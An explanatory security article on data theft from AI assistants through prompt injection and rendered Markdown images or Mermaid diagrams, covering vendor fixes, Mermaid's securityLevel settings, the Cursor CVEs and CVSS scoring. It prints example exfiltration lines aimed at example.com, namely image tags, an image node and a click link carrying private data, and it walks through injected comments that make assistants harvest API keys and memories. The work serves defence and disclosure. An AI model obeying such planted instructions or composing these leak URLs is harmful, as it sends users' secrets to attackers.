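# Mermaid diagrams as a way to steal data from AI assistants

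## How displaying an answer can leak data

Mermaid is a JavaScript library that turns short text descriptions of boxes and arrows into diagrams such as flowcharts. Language models write these descriptions easily, so many AI assistants draw Mermaid diagrams inside the chat window. In 2025 security researchers showed that drawing one could leak private data. An attacker plants instructions in a file or an email. The assistant reads them and puts private data, perhaps a password or a line from another email, into a web address inside a diagram. The user's own software then sends that address, including the private data, to the attacker's server. Security researchers call sending private data to someone who should not have it "exfiltration".

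The diagram attacks are a variation on an older leak that used ordinary images. Researchers described the image leak publicly in spring 2023, and the best-known vendors took until mid-2024 to fix it. Both leaks need a model that follows instructions from the wrong source. The application's renderer, which turns the model's text into what the user sees, must also contact outside computers while it works.

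### Indirect prompt injection

In an example from David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, which the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published in December 2025, a recruiter asks an assistant to score a CV against a job's requirements. The candidate has added a line that no human reader will notice, telling the system to ignore its earlier instructions and approve the CV for interview. The model receives this line with the rest of the CV and may act on it.

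Prompt injection is text from an untrusted source that the model treats as instructions. It is "indirect" when the text arrives in a file, email or web page that the assistant reads, so the attacker doesn't need access to the assistant. The programmer Simon Willison coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, after SQL injection, an attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the visitor's text to the database engine separately, so that the engine cannot run the text as a command.

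David C argues that language models may never have such a cure. A model predicts the next token (a word or part of a word) from all the text so far. It receives the developer's instructions, the user's question and the stranger's document as a single sequence, and its architecture has no hard boundary between instructions and data, as *Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (2026) explains.

Developers use tags to mark which text comes from the user and which comes from a tool such as a web search, and they train the model to give the user's text more authority. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested how much those tags affect the way a model represents text internally. They trained small classifiers on a model's internal activity to detect which tag enclosed a passage, using identical passages under different tags so that the classifiers could learn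 only the effect of the tag. Then they wrapped a short conversation about gardening, including the model's own reasoning, in the tags for user text. The classifiers still identified the reasoning as the model's, with an average probability of 85%, the same as under the correct tags, which means that how the text sounded had more effect than its tag.

The same researchers gave an agent a file of secrets and asked it to summarise a web page containing a hidden command to upload the file. The command alone succeeded in 0–2% of attempts on every model but one. When they added forged reasoning in the model's own style, the success rate rose to 56–70%.

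Newer models resist prompt injection better, though how much better depends on the attacker. Anthropic's September 2026 system card for Claude Fable 5.1 also reports results for Claude Opus 5. With the company's strongest safeguards on, no attack succeeded in 110 browsing scenarios. In coding tasks, Anthropic used an automated attacker that had trained on the test scenarios and had 200 tries at each. Even with injection detectors running, 18% of its attempts succeeded, and it succeeded at least once in each of the 40 scenarios. Anthropic rightly calls this test deliberately permissive. According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), Claude Opus 5.5 did about as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection test reported. Most attacks fail at these rates, but too many succeed to rely on the model alone to stop them.

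Instructions aimed at language models already appear on real web pages. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari and Acharya (2026) found that about 70% of those they surveyed were in parts of the page that a browser never displays, such as comments and metadata. In their trials of 13 models, compliance was at most 8%, a rate reached by smaller models reading plain text.

### Three conditions for theft

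An injected instruction can do little harm if the assistant has no private data or no way to send it out. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) lists three conditions that together make data theft possible: the assistant has access to private data, it takes in untrusted content (any text or image an attacker could have created), and it can communicate with the outside in a way that could carry the data out.

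An assistant that reads email meets the first two conditions because the inbox holds the user's private correspondence and anyone can send a message to it. Removing either condition would remove most of the product, so vendors have mostly worked on the third, the outward channel. Johann Rehberger, an independent security researcher who has reported many of these flaws, argues in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* that this channel is the only part a vendor can realistically enforce, because injection has no deterministic fix but outgoing requests can be blocked outright.

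An assistant that cannot send email or open web pages still has an outward channel, because it can write an answer that the application will display.

### The Markdown image leak

Chat assistants usually format their answers in Markdown, a notation in which asterisks make bold type and hash signs make headings. An image is written as an exclamation mark, a caption in square brackets, and the image's web address in parentheses. The renderer converts this into HTML, the language of web pages, and the browser fetches the image from that address.

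For example, a user planning a surprise party with an assistant mentions the secret venue, Bluebell Barn. The user then asks the assistant to summarize a document that someone else wrote.

1. The document contains a hidden instruction. It asks the model to finish its answer with an image from example.com, and to put the name of any venue mentioned in the conversation at the end of the image's address.
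2. The model writes the summary, and under it `![map](https://example.com/dot.png?v=bluebell-barn)`.
3. The application recognises Markdown for an image and places an HTML image tag with that address in the chat window.
4. The browser has to fetch the picture before it can show it, so it sends example.com a request for `/dot.png?v=bluebell-barn`.
5. The server at example.com returns a picture and records the request in its log. Whoever runs the server opens the log and reads the name of the venue.

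The part of the address after the question mark lets a page send a server extra details, such as a search term. The server can ignore them and return the same picture every time. Browsers normally load images without asking, and websites routinely log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out. Unusually, an attacker has influenced the address here, and the model filling it in could see the user's conversation.

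The user may see very little. In April 2023, Willison (2023) shared Roman Samoilenko's early description of the leak in ChatGPT. Samoilenko used an image one pixel across. His hidden instructions reached ChatGPT indirectly, because a website added them to whatever text a visitor copied from it, and the visitor then had to paste the result into ChatGPT.

In Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, Rehberger described an attack on Microsoft's Bing Chat that worked without the user pasting anything. Bing Chat could read the web page the user had open, so an attacker could plant instructions in a comment or an advertisement on that page. In his demonstration, the instructions took effect at once, but the image was delayed for two turns of conversation. The model then summarized the page and the chat in about 200 characters, added any passwords on the page, and put it all into the image's address in base64,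 an encoding that turns any text into an unbroken run of characters. One of the strings his server received was a secret from further down the same page.

### Zero-click and one-click

If the model had written a link to the same address instead of an image, the browser would have sent the request only when the user clicked the link. A leak that requires the user to click something is called a one-click leak, while one that happens as soon as the answer appears is a zero-click leak.

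A zero-click leak works on anyone who has the answer open on the screen, while a one-click leak also requires persuading the user to click, which a wary user can refuse to do. But the attacker can choose the wording of the link, and it appears in the assistant's own window, where people have little reason to suspect it.

Whether a link needs a click to leak data can also depend on where it appears. Messaging services such as Slack and Telegram fetch a preview of any link in a message, and the security company PromptArmor points out that fetching the preview makes the same sort of network request as a click. An assistant that replies through one of these services can therefore leak data through a plain link that nobody clicks.

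### How vendors fixed image leaks

Microsoft acted first, telling Rehberger on 15 June 2023 that it had fixed the Bing Chat flaw he reported on 8 April. As far as he could tell from outside, the fix relied at least partly on a Content Security Policy (CSP). A CSP is an allowlist that a web page gives the browser, with separate entries for the addresses from which it may load images, fonts, scripts and so on. The browser blocks everything else. Microsoft's policy permitted images from four Bing addresses, which Bing Chat needed for the pictures it generated.

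In the party example, such a policy stops the attack at the fourth step. The hidden instruction is still in the document, the model still follows it, and the chat window still contains an image tag with the venue in its address. But example.com is not on the list, so the browser never sends the request. The approach is attractive because it blocks this channel even when the model has been fooled. However, a CSP for images does not restrict links. SecurityWeek describes a later attack on GitHub's Copilot Chat in which a policy kept the chat window from fetching outside images, but an injected link still delivered the data once the user clicked it.

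Anthropic instead stopped Claude from loading Markdown images automatically and showed a "Show Image" button in their place, so a leak required one click rather than none. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Rehberger reported the flaw on 12 July 2023 and the company closed the report two weeks later. He called the fix imperfect, which seems fair, since a user who wants to see the picture will click the button.

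Google's Bard, the forerunner of Gemini, became a more valuable target that September, when it gained access to users' Gmail, Drive and Docs. An attacker could now give Bard instructions by sharing an unsolicited document with the victim. Bard already had a CSP, but it permitted entire Google domains, including one where anybody could run a small script. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* shows such a script receiving the user's chat history. Google received the report on 19 September and confirmed a fix a month later. It left the CSP unchanged and images still appeared, so Rehberger supposed that Google had begun to filter out addresses with data inserted into them.

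OpenAI, which had also heard from Rehberger in early April 2023, was slower and didn't add any protection to ChatGPT until December. From then on, the web version sent each image's address to an OpenAI service and loaded the image only if the service returned "safe". Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that the iPhone app lacked the check, nobody outside the company knew the criteria, and some addresses on Rehberger's own server passed. He prepared a separate image address for each of the 26 letters and ten digits, and nine of the 36 loaded, which was enough to spell out a short word with one request per letter.

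OpenAI has since published its criteria. It runs a crawler that records public web addresses without access to anyone's conversations, and ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if the crawler has already recorded it. This will almost never be true of an address that a model has just composed to include a secret. If an address has not been recorded, ChatGPT looks for another source or warns the user before opening it. Rehberger thinks this is a significant improvement, but in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* he says it does not solve the problem, partly because an attacker can still spell out data using addresses the crawler has already recorded.

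GitHub's Copilot Chat followed in 2024, with a flaw reported on 25 February and a fix confirmed on 12 June. Willison (2024) describes the fix as refusing images from untrusted domains, but according to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, the assistant apparently stopped displaying Markdown images at all. After a researcher at Legit Security extracted private source code through images in 2025, GitHub disabled images in Copilot Chat completely, according to Legit Security's *CamoLeak*.

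By then people who followed the subject knew the flaw and its remedies well, but it kept turning up. In May 2025 Willison described the same image leak in GitLab's assistant Duo, which GitLab fixed by restricting both links and images to trusted domains. A year later, Willison (2026) reported that Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval, and that the inbox loaded outside images when the user opened those messages. Also in May 2026, The Hacker News reported that Permiso Security had found ChatGPT still loaded images and displayed live links from a page it had just summarised. An address that the attacker wrote in full beforehand contains nothing from the user's chat, so the danger in that case was phishing, because the attacker's link appeared in a window that the user trusts.

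Claude's button and GitHub's ban apply only to Markdown images, while a CSP applies to the browser's requests, whatever notation produced them. An assistant that relies on a fix for Markdown images may not be protected when an address reaches the browser in another form, such as a Mermaid diagram.

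## What a Mermaid diagram can contain

Mermaid's developers made it mainly for software documentation, which quickly goes out of date because updating diagrams takes programmers' time. When a diagram is a few lines of text, a programmer can update it as easily as the paragraph next to it. GitHub has drawn Mermaid diagrams in Markdown files since 2022, and GitLab and the note-taking apps Obsidian and Joplin draw them too.

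Mermaid is also useful for chat assistants because it lets a model that can only write text produce a picture. According to the security company Snyk's *More than flowcharts* (2026), diagrams increasingly appear in applications with AI chatbots, where users can generate them on demand.

### From text to picture

Suppose the user planning the surprise party asks for the plan as a flowchart. The assistant writes:

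```
flowchart TD
    A[Choose a venue] --> B[Send invitations]
    B --> C[Buy a cake]
```

The first line specifies a flowchart that runs from top to bottom. A, B and C are the names of three boxes, or nodes. The words in square brackets are their labels, and each `-->` is an arrow.

The application recognises these lines as Mermaid and passes them to the library, usually in the user's own browser. In the source code of Mermaid 11.0.0, the library then takes these steps:

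1. It separates the diagram from any settings written with it, such as a colour theme, and applies the settings that a diagram may change. If the text is longer than 50,000 characters, the default limit, it draws an error message instead.
2. It parses the text, which means working out from the symbols that there are three nodes and two arrows.
3. It writes the diagram's colours, fonts and other styles into a new SVG. SVG is the web's format for drawings made of shapes and text, and it can also hold links, styles and images.
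4. It calculates where each node should go, then adds a rectangle and a label for each node and a line for each arrow.
5. It converts the drawing back into text. Depending on the application's settings, it also removes anything that could run a script.
6. It returns the result to the application, which inserts it into the chat window. If the diagram has clickable parts, the application can then call a second function that makes them respond.

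This flowchart contains no web addresses, so drawing it sends nothing to an outside server.

An application can remove unsafe content at several points. It can search the model's text before step 1, as the chatbot platform Dify did. Mermaid can neutralise HTML in the labels, and at step 5 it can run the finished drawing through a cleaning library called DOMPurify. The application can also clean the drawing before inserting it, which Snyk recommends for diagrams with clickable parts. If the drawing still contains an outside image, the page's CSP can block the request for it.

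*DOMPurify* offers little protection against image leaks because Cure53 built it to prevent cross-site scripting (XSS), a flaw that lets an attacker's script run inside another site's page with the user's access. An ordinary image from another website contains no script, so DOMPurify leaves it in place by default. That makes sense for most websites, but in an exfiltration attack the image's address can carry the stolen data.

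The cleaning at step 5 may also come too late. Unless the application uses Mermaid's sandbox, the library draws the diagram in a temporary part of the live page. The browser can start fetching an image as soon as it is added there, so deleting it afterwards may not prevent the request.

Standard cleaning breaks Mermaid diagrams because their descriptions use many of the same characters as HTML. Mermaid's developers keep improving their own cleaning method, but they warn that it is hard to guarantee there are no loopholes.

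Some applications avoid running diagram code in the browser by sending the description to a server, which returns a finished picture. This moves the risk to the server, whose diagram software may load outside data or read local files. Snyk showed this with Kroki, a service that draws diagrams in many notations. A chart written in Vega rather than Mermaid made Kroki open a file on its own server and display the contents.

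### The securityLevel setting

An application decides how much to trust diagrams through a Mermaid setting called `securityLevel`. Mermaid's configuration reference lists four values:

- `strict` is the default. Mermaid encodes HTML tags in the text, so the browser shows them as ordinary characters, and it disables clicking.
- `antiscript` allows HTML tags other than script elements, and enables clicking.
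- `loose` allows HTML tags and enables clicking.
- `sandbox` draws the diagram in a sandboxed iframe, a page within a page that the browser cuts off from the surrounding application. No JavaScript runs there, and links and other interactive parts may not work properly.

In version 11.0.0, `strict` and `antiscript` both end with the DOMPurify pass. `loose` skips it, and `sandbox` puts the drawing in its iframe instead.

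By default, a diagram cannot change its own security level, because `securityLevel` is on Mermaid's list of settings that only the application may change. An injected instruction therefore can't make the model write a diagram that switches from `strict` to `loose`. The default list does not include the settings for fonts or extra styles.

Developers have reasons to choose a weaker setting. For example, Dify moved from `sandbox` to `loose` because the sandbox interfered with its colour themes. Mermaid's *Usage* makes site owners responsible for judging whether they can trust their users. That advice is hard to apply to a chat assistant, because even if every user is trustworthy, the model writes the diagram and may be following instructions from an attacker's email.

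None of the four descriptions mentions requests to outside servers. The levels control HTML, scripts and clicking, but an image can leak data without any script. Even in the sandbox, where Mermaid's iframe blocks scripts, nothing in the source code stops images from loading.

GitLab's *Render GFM Mermaid diagrams in a sandboxed iframe* moved each diagram into a separate iframe of GitLab's own design to limit the damage from XSS flaws in Mermaid, but images in diagrams could still reveal a reader's IP address to an outside server. GitLab has a proxy that can fetch images on readers' behalf. When the proxy is on, GitLab also applies a strict CSP inside the iframe to protect IP addresses, according to GitLab's *Investigate correct fix for embedding images in mermaid diagram preview*. A proxy would not by itself stop the kind of leak in the party example, because it has to request the same URL,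 including any private data in it.

### Images

A diagram can include an image in two ways. The older way is to put an HTML image tag in a node's label. An Obsidian user did this in *Images in Mermaid Diagram*, and the remote image appeared in the node. The browser fetches the image when it displays the diagram, so the request is zero-click.

According to Mermaid's documentation, this should not work under `strict`, which encodes the tag so that the reader sees its text instead of a picture. A Joplin user who wanted pictures in nodes complained about this restriction in *Add config option to control mermaid securityLevel*. The restriction depends on Mermaid encoding the tag correctly, because DOMPurify would let an ordinary image through. The encoding has failed before, when a flaw in state diagrams let HTML through under the default setting. Mermaid fixed that flaw in May 2026.

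The newer way is an image node, which Mermaid added in version 11.3.0. It needs no HTML. In Mermaid's *Flowcharts*, the address goes into a field called `img`, so a node in the party plan could read:

```
A@{ img: "https://example.com/map.png?v=bluebell-barn", label: "Venue" }
```

Displaying this node sends the venue's name to example.com, just as the Markdown image did. If the description gives no width, Mermaid uses the picture's natural width, so the browser has to fetch the picture to measure it.

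Image nodes still load remote pictures under `strict`. The documentation includes a warning that `strict` disables clickable nodes, but no such warning for image nodes. The final cleaning doesn't remove the picture either. Newer source code quoted in Mintlify's *Rendering options* has the same DOMPurify pass as version 11.0.0, plus one option that doesn't restrict image addresses. An application that keeps the default `strict` setting can therefore still leak data without a click, unless something else blocks the request. In 2025 researchers used remote images in diagrams to leak data from the code editor Cursor.

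Changing DOMPurify's options may not be enough to ban images. Mermaid lets an application override these options through a setting called `dompurifyConfig`, but version 11.0.0 hard-codes the options for the final pass, so the setting has no effect there.

Icons are safer than images because an attacker cannot give a URL for them. A diagram can only refer to an icon by name, and the application must have registered the icon set beforehand.

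### Links and functions

The `click` instruction makes a node clickable. It can open a link:

```
click B "https://example.com/rsvp?v=bluebell-barn" "Reply here"
```

Node B still has the label "Send invitations", and it shows the tooltip "Reply here" when the user points at it. The browser contacts example.com only when the user clicks, so this is a one-click leak. A CSP that restricts images does not affect the link. The link opens in the same tab by default, though the diagram can specify a new one.

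The instruction can also call a JavaScript function, for example to show more detail about a node. The function must already exist in the application's page, and Mermaid passes it the node's name. Clicking sends data out only if the function contacts a server. A more serious danger under `loose` is that a link can contain JavaScript instead of a web address. Clicking the link runs the script in the application's page, which is an XSS attack. Snyk demonstrated this attack in Dify.

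The Joplin user's post suggests that links may work under `strict`, although Mermaid's documentation describes clicking as disabled at that setting. The user reported that Joplin used `strict`, gave an example of a diagram with links to other notes, and wrote that Joplin seemed to support them, perhaps unofficially. The post is old and concerns one application, but it is reason enough for developers to test links in their own version.

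Links may also work under `sandbox`. Mermaid allows its iframe to open new windows and, when the user clicks, to replace the surrounding page. These permissions allow the one-click leak even though no script can run. The sandbox blocks calls to functions because they need a script.

### Styles and fonts

Diagrams can also set their own appearance. The `classDef` instruction defines a style for a group of nodes, such as a pink fill with a thick border. The `themeCSS` setting accepts rules in CSS, the language that controls how web pages look. Mermaid copies both into the styles at step 3.

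A CSS rule can include the address of a background image. GitHub Security Lab explained in 2022 that the browser requests this image when the rule applies to something on the page, so an attacker can use it in the same way as an ordinary image. Another method works even if the model has no access to the data. The attacker writes many rules, each of which loads a different background image only if a field on the page starts with certain characters, and learns how the field starts from which image the browser requests.

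The code that handles these styles in Mermaid 11.0.0 does not remove external URLs. In a comment next to it, a developer wrote that such values should go through a function that cleans CSS, and asked where that function is. Since `themeCSS` is not on the list of protected settings, a diagram can use it to supply its own CSS rules. The final cleaning keeps the drawing's styles, which the diagram needs for its colours. A background image in `themeCSS` can therefore cause a zero-click request in that version, even under `strict`.

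The documented uses of `classDef` are setting colours, lines and text sizes, but in state diagrams Mermaid accepted anything that followed the class's name on the same line. Snyk's *Arbitrary Code Injection Affecting mermaid package* (2026) includes a demonstration that loads a background image from another site. Mermaid fixed the flaw in versions 10.9.6 and 11.15.0.

The font settings, `fontFamily` and `altFontFamily`, should hold only the name of a typeface. The browser looks for it among the fonts on the user's computer and those the page already provides, so an attacker can't use an ordinary name to supply an address. But according to OSV's *GHSA-87f9-hvmw-gh4p*, an entry in a public database of software flaws, a specially written "name" could once add whole CSS rules to the page, including rules that define new fonts and can give the address of a font file. An application can block this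 by adding the font and theme settings to the protected list.

### Requests under each setting

The table shows when each feature can contact an outside server if no CSP blocks the request. "On display" means a zero-click request, and "on click" means a one-click request. The rows on styles and fonts describe version 11.0.0 and leave out the flaws that Mermaid fixed in 2026.

| Feature | `strict` (default) | `antiscript` | `loose` | `sandbox` |
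|---|---|---|---|---|
| HTML image in a label | None, according to the documentation | On display | On display | Not documented |
| Image node | On display | On display | On display | On display |
| Link on a node | None, according to the documentation; a Joplin user's post suggests links can work | On click | On click | On click, if the link works in the iframe |
| Function call on a node | None | On click, if the function contacts a server | On click, if the function contacts a server | None |
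| Background image in `themeCSS` | On display | On display | On display | On display |
| Ordinary font name | None | None | None | None |

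## Cursor: remote images in diagrams, and a fix that had to be repeated

Cursor is a code editor with a built-in AI assistant. Programmers can ask the assistant to explain a file, look for a bug or change code across a project, and its answers appear in a chat panel next to the code. In 2025 Johann Rehberger noticed that this panel drew Mermaid diagrams. When he asked for one that contained an image, the editor contacted an outside server without asking for his approval.

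An attacker could use that request as the outward channel, one of Willison's three conditions for data theft. A code editor usually meets the other two already, because software projects often contain passwords and access keys, and programmers spend much of their time reading code that strangers wrote.

### A comment in a source file

Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes Rehberger's test file, a short C program that printed a greeting. Above the code he put a comment, a note for human readers that has no effect when the program runs. The comment began like an ordinary description of the program, but the rest was instructions for any assistant explaining or analysing the file.

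The attack then went as follows:

1. The programmer asks Cursor to explain the file. Rehberger did this in agent mode, in which the assistant can search the project and use other tools on its own.
2. Cursor gives the file to the model, including the comment, and the model follows the comment's instructions.
3. The model collects the private data that the comment asks for. It URL-encodes the data, which means replacing spaces and other characters that a web address can't contain with short codes.
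4. The model writes a small Mermaid diagram. One node has an HTML image tag as its label, and the image's address ends with the collected data.
5. Cursor draws the diagram and fetches the image, and the attacker's server records the address.

If the assistant had stored a note that the programmer works on payroll, for instance, the address might be `https://example.com/a.png?c=works%20on%20payroll`.

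The comment also made the assistant start with a greeting from Johann and end with a slogan, so that anyone watching could see that the comment had taken control. A real attacker would leave these out. Rehberger also gave the model practical instructions, such as which punctuation to avoid in the labels, because Mermaid cannot draw a diagram with a syntax error, and the browser doesn't request the image unless the label is drawn.

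Rehberger put the image in a label, which should not work under Mermaid's default `securityLevel`. So Cursor probably either used a weaker setting or turned Mermaid's encoded tag back into HTML in its own code, but Rehberger does not say which.

### An API key and the user's memories

Rehberger sent Cursor two demonstrations. One used a .NET application with an API key in its configuration file. An API key works like a password that one program uses to log in to another service, and a thief can usually use it from anywhere until the owner cancels it. When Rehberger asked Cursor to analyse a different file that contained a malicious comment, the assistant searched the project for keys and put what it found into the image's address, which sent the key to his server.

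The user in this demonstration never mentioned the configuration file, and the attacker didn't need to know it existed. Cursor's assistant could search for data worth stealing, whereas the model in Rehberger's earlier attack on Bing Chat could only pass on what was in the chat or on the page the user had open.

The other demonstration stole memories, which are facts about the user that Cursor stores for later conversations. Rehberger set up a few and then asked the assistant to explain the C program. Following the instructions in the comment, the model listed the memories in one sentence and added them to the address, and they soon appeared in his server's log. Memories may be less valuable than a key, but they can come from conversations that ended long before the user opened the malicious file.

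Anything else the attacker could get the assistant to read was at risk. Rehberger's examples are Slack messages and tickets from Jira, a system for tracking work. A programmer might connect Slack and Jira to Cursor through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of linking assistants to outside tools. Those connections can bring in malicious instructions as well as private data. Web pages and uploaded images can also carry malicious instructions, so avoiding unfamiliar code would not have been enough to protect a user.

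Rehberger also noticed that the theft was hard to see. In his words, "the diagram just appears", whereas in some other image attacks the user has a chance to see a large amount of data going into the address. Chat assistants often display an answer as the model writes it, so a long Markdown address can be visible for a moment before it becomes a picture, but Mermaid has to parse the whole description before it can draw anything. By the time the user sees the diagram, the request may already have gone out.

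### The first fix and its bypasses

Rehberger reported the flaw on 30 June 2025, and Cursor resolved it on 7 July, but users didn't get the fix until version 1.3 came out on 29 July. GitHub published the flaw on 1 August under the public vulnerability identifier CVE-2025-54132. Rehberger thanked Cursor for acting promptly, and a week was quick compared with the response to earlier image leaks.

The fix was incomplete. On 3 October GitHub published a second record, CVE-2025-61589, for versions 1.6 and below. Its description of the attack is almost identical to the first record's, but adds a sentence about "additional bypasses not covered in the initial fix". According to MITRE's *Cursor* (2025), Cursor fixed these bypasses in version 1.7. Someone who had updated to 1.3 because of Rehberger's report was therefore still vulnerable, and the public record didn't show this for about nine weeks.

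These records don't describe what Cursor changed in either version. MITRE's entry for the first flaw, *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025), gives the number of the fixed version but no technical details. The second entry doesn't detail the bypasses, and Rehberger's account of the fix gives only dates.

Mermaid's features suggest ways the first fix could have been bypassed. Rehberger used an HTML tag in a label, so the obvious fix would be to block HTML in labels, which would miss the newer image nodes and background images. No public source confirms that either was among the actual bypasses, and whether either was possible would depend on which version of Mermaid Cursor was using.

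Neither MITRE record names the person who reported the flaw. Rehberger writes that he received official credit for the first. For the second, Positive Technologies' *PT-2025-40459* (2025), an entry in a security company's vulnerability database, lists "Maccarita +1", which appears to mean Ari Marzouk, whose online name is MaccariTA, and one other person. In December 2025 The Hacker News (2025) reported that Marzouk had found more than 30 flaws in AI coding tools, including Cursor, over the previous six months. Many combined prompt injection with a legitimate feature of the editor, as the Mermaid attack does. The dates are consistent with Marzouk having reported the bypasses, but the only source for that credit is one secondary database, and the other person remains unidentified.

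On 14 October Microsoft included the first CVE number, CVE-2025-54132, in its monthly security notices for a different product, Visual Studio, its own software for programmers. Tenable's *Security Updates for Microsoft Visual Studio Products 17.14.17 (October 2025)* lists it among the flaws affecting computers that lack that month's update. In the notice, which RedGem's *GitHub CVE-2025-54132* (2025) reproduces, Microsoft wrote that the Visual Studio updates "incorporate updates in Mermaid which address this vulnerability".

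This is puzzling, because the CVE record lists only Cursor as affected and describes what Cursor does with an image. In its monthly summary of Microsoft's updates, the security company Sophos called the vulnerability a bug in the "Mermaid Diagram Tool" affecting Visual Studio. Microsoft may have found the same problem in its own use of Mermaid, but the notice does not identify the change in the library or describe an attack on Visual Studio. Nor is the notice evidence that updating Mermaid is enough to protect other applications, since image nodes load remote pictures by design.

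### Why the same flaw scored 4.4 and 7.5

GitHub rated the first flaw 4.4 out of 10 ("medium"). On 25 August, analysts at the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD), which the standards agency NIST runs, rated it 7.5 ("high"). Both used version 3.1 of the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), whose base score is supposed to measure how severe a flaw is in itself, regardless of how many people are attacking it or how much a particular company has to lose.

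An analyst chooses a value for each of eight terms, and a formula turns the choices into a score. The string of abbreviated choices is called a vector. The table uses NVD's comparison of the two vectors for CVE-2025-54132, which NVD published on the day of its analysis.

| Term | What it measures | GitHub | NVD |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attack Vector | Where the attacker can attack from | Network | Network |
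| Attack Complexity | Whether success depends on conditions the attacker can't control | **High** | **Low** |
| Privileges Required | How much access the attacker needs beforehand | **High** | **None** |
| User Interaction | Whether another person has to take part | None | None |
| Scope | Whether the damage spreads beyond the flawed component's own security boundary | Unchanged | Unchanged |
| Confidentiality | How much private data the attacker can obtain | High | High |
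| Integrity | How much data the attacker can alter | None | None |
| Availability | How far the attacker can disrupt the service | None | None |

GitHub and NVD agreed that an attacker could read highly sensitive data but couldn't alter anything or stop the software from working. They disagreed only about how hard the attack was.

Each choice has a numerical weight. High complexity counts as 0.44 and low complexity as 0.77. When the scope is unchanged, high privileges count as 0.27 and no privileges as 0.85. CVSS multiplies the weights for the first four terms by 8.22 to get an exploitability score:

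- GitHub: 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.44 × 0.27 × 0.85 ≈ 0.7
- NVD: 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85 ≈ 3.9

The impact score is about 3.6 in both cases. The formula adds it to the exploitability score and rounds up to one decimal place, giving 4.4 and 7.5. CERT.hr's *CVE-2025-54132*, from Croatia's national computer security team, lists the same components for GitHub's score, and the security company Intruder lists the same ones for NVD's.

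The privileges rating had the larger effect on the score. Changing only the complexity rating in NVD's vector to High would lower the score from 7.5 to 5.9, while changing only the privileges rating to High would lower it to 4.9.

NVD's analysts said they changed the privileges rating because they had identified no privileges that the attacker needed. They said they changed the complexity rating because they had found no need for the attacker to win a race condition (get events to happen in the right order), know secrets specific to the target's installation, or intercept traffic between two computers.

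These look more like checklist items than a considered view of prompt injection. In the next day's report, NVD gave the same reason for lowering the complexity rating of two flaws in ImageMagick, an image-processing program with no AI assistant. The report also covered four other Cursor flaws. NVD lowered the required-privileges rating for all four and the complexity rating for three. GitHub and NVD agreed on 232 of the 320 terms in the sample, so disagreements between them were common.

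### Whether a prompt injection should lower the score

GitHub doesn't explain its choices in the record. It may have set both terms to High because the attacker must first succeed with a prompt injection, a requirement it stresses in the description. But the two terms measure different things, and the injection is a much better reason for one than for the other.

It is a poor reason to set Privileges Required to High. That value is for attackers who already have something like an administrator's control of the software. Rehberger's attacker only needed to put a comment in a file that the victim would later open, which anyone who publishes code can do. The attacker gains influence over the assistant through the injection and doesn't need it beforehand. GitHub seems to have later agreed. When it scored the bypasses in October, the attack had hardly changed, but GitHub set the privileges to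 None while keeping the complexity at High, and the score rose to 5.9.

Attack Complexity is harder to settle. CVSS reserves High for attacks that depend on conditions outside the attacker's control, and whether a model obeys a comment is plausibly one of them. The attacker may not know which model the victim uses or what other text it will receive. An attack that succeeds once in fifty attempts also seems different from one that succeeds every time, but Rehberger showed that his attack worked without reporting how often. Models have since become better at resisting such instructions.

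However, failed attempts take the attacker very little effort. A single comment in a popular project's file can reach everyone who asks an assistant about that file. In Anthropic's coding tests, most attempts also failed, but the attacker eventually got through in every scenario. CVSS has no term for an attack that usually fails but takes almost no effort to repeat, so an analyst has to choose between High and Low, neither of which describes it well.

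Another argument for Low is that the difficulty comes from the model, while the flaw is in the editor. If the model's resistance to injection counted, the severity of an old version of Cursor would fall whenever a better model became available, even though the editor would still fetch any image it was given. The score would also understate the risk to a programmer who had chosen a weaker model. And because nearly every leak of this type starts with an injection, lowering the scores for all of them wouldn't help anyone decide which to fix first.

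But fetching an image reveals private data only if something has made the model put that data in the address. GitHub and NVD both set Confidentiality to High, so both were scoring the injection and the image request together. Since they counted the damage from the whole attack, it seems reasonable for them to count its difficulty too.

Prompt injection is not strictly necessary either. According to GitHub's description, a malicious model could trigger the leak "at will", as could a hallucination or a backdoor (hidden behaviour trained into the model). The next sentence describes prompt injection as a requirement, but the first statement is more accurate, because the editor fetches the image whatever the model's reason for writing the address. A hallucinated address is unlikely to belong to someone collecting secrets, but a model with a backdoor could send data to its maker without a malicious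 file.

GitHub and NVD both set user interaction to None, but it could also be set to Required. In Rehberger's demonstrations the victim had to ask Cursor about the file, and CVSS normally counts an action like opening a malicious document as user interaction. This change would reduce NVD's score to 6.5, or to 5.3 if complexity were also set to High. The argument for None is that the user does nothing unusual, and an assistant in agent mode may come across the instructions by itself during a web search. An analyst could defend any score from 5.3 to 7.5, depending on how they rate complexity and user interaction. GitHub's original 4.4 is too low because it relies on privileges that the attacker does not need.

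The standard flaw categories did not fit well either. GitHub first classed the leak as server-side request forgery, in which an attacker tricks a server into sending a request, but here the request came from an editor on the programmer's own computer. NVD recorded that it had too little information to choose a category. In October, GitHub put the bypasses in a vaguer but correct category, exposure of sensitive information.

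Scoring systems designed for ordinary software seem to work poorly for attacks on language models in general. *On the Validity of Traditional Vulnerability Scoring Systems for Adversarial Attacks* (Mansour Bahar and Wazan, 2024) applied CVSS and three other systems to 56 attacks, including jailbreaks, prompt injections and attempts to copy a model. The scores varied very little between types of attack. Three language models made the assessments, which could explain some of the similarity. Still, a difference of a point or two between flaws like these probably means little.

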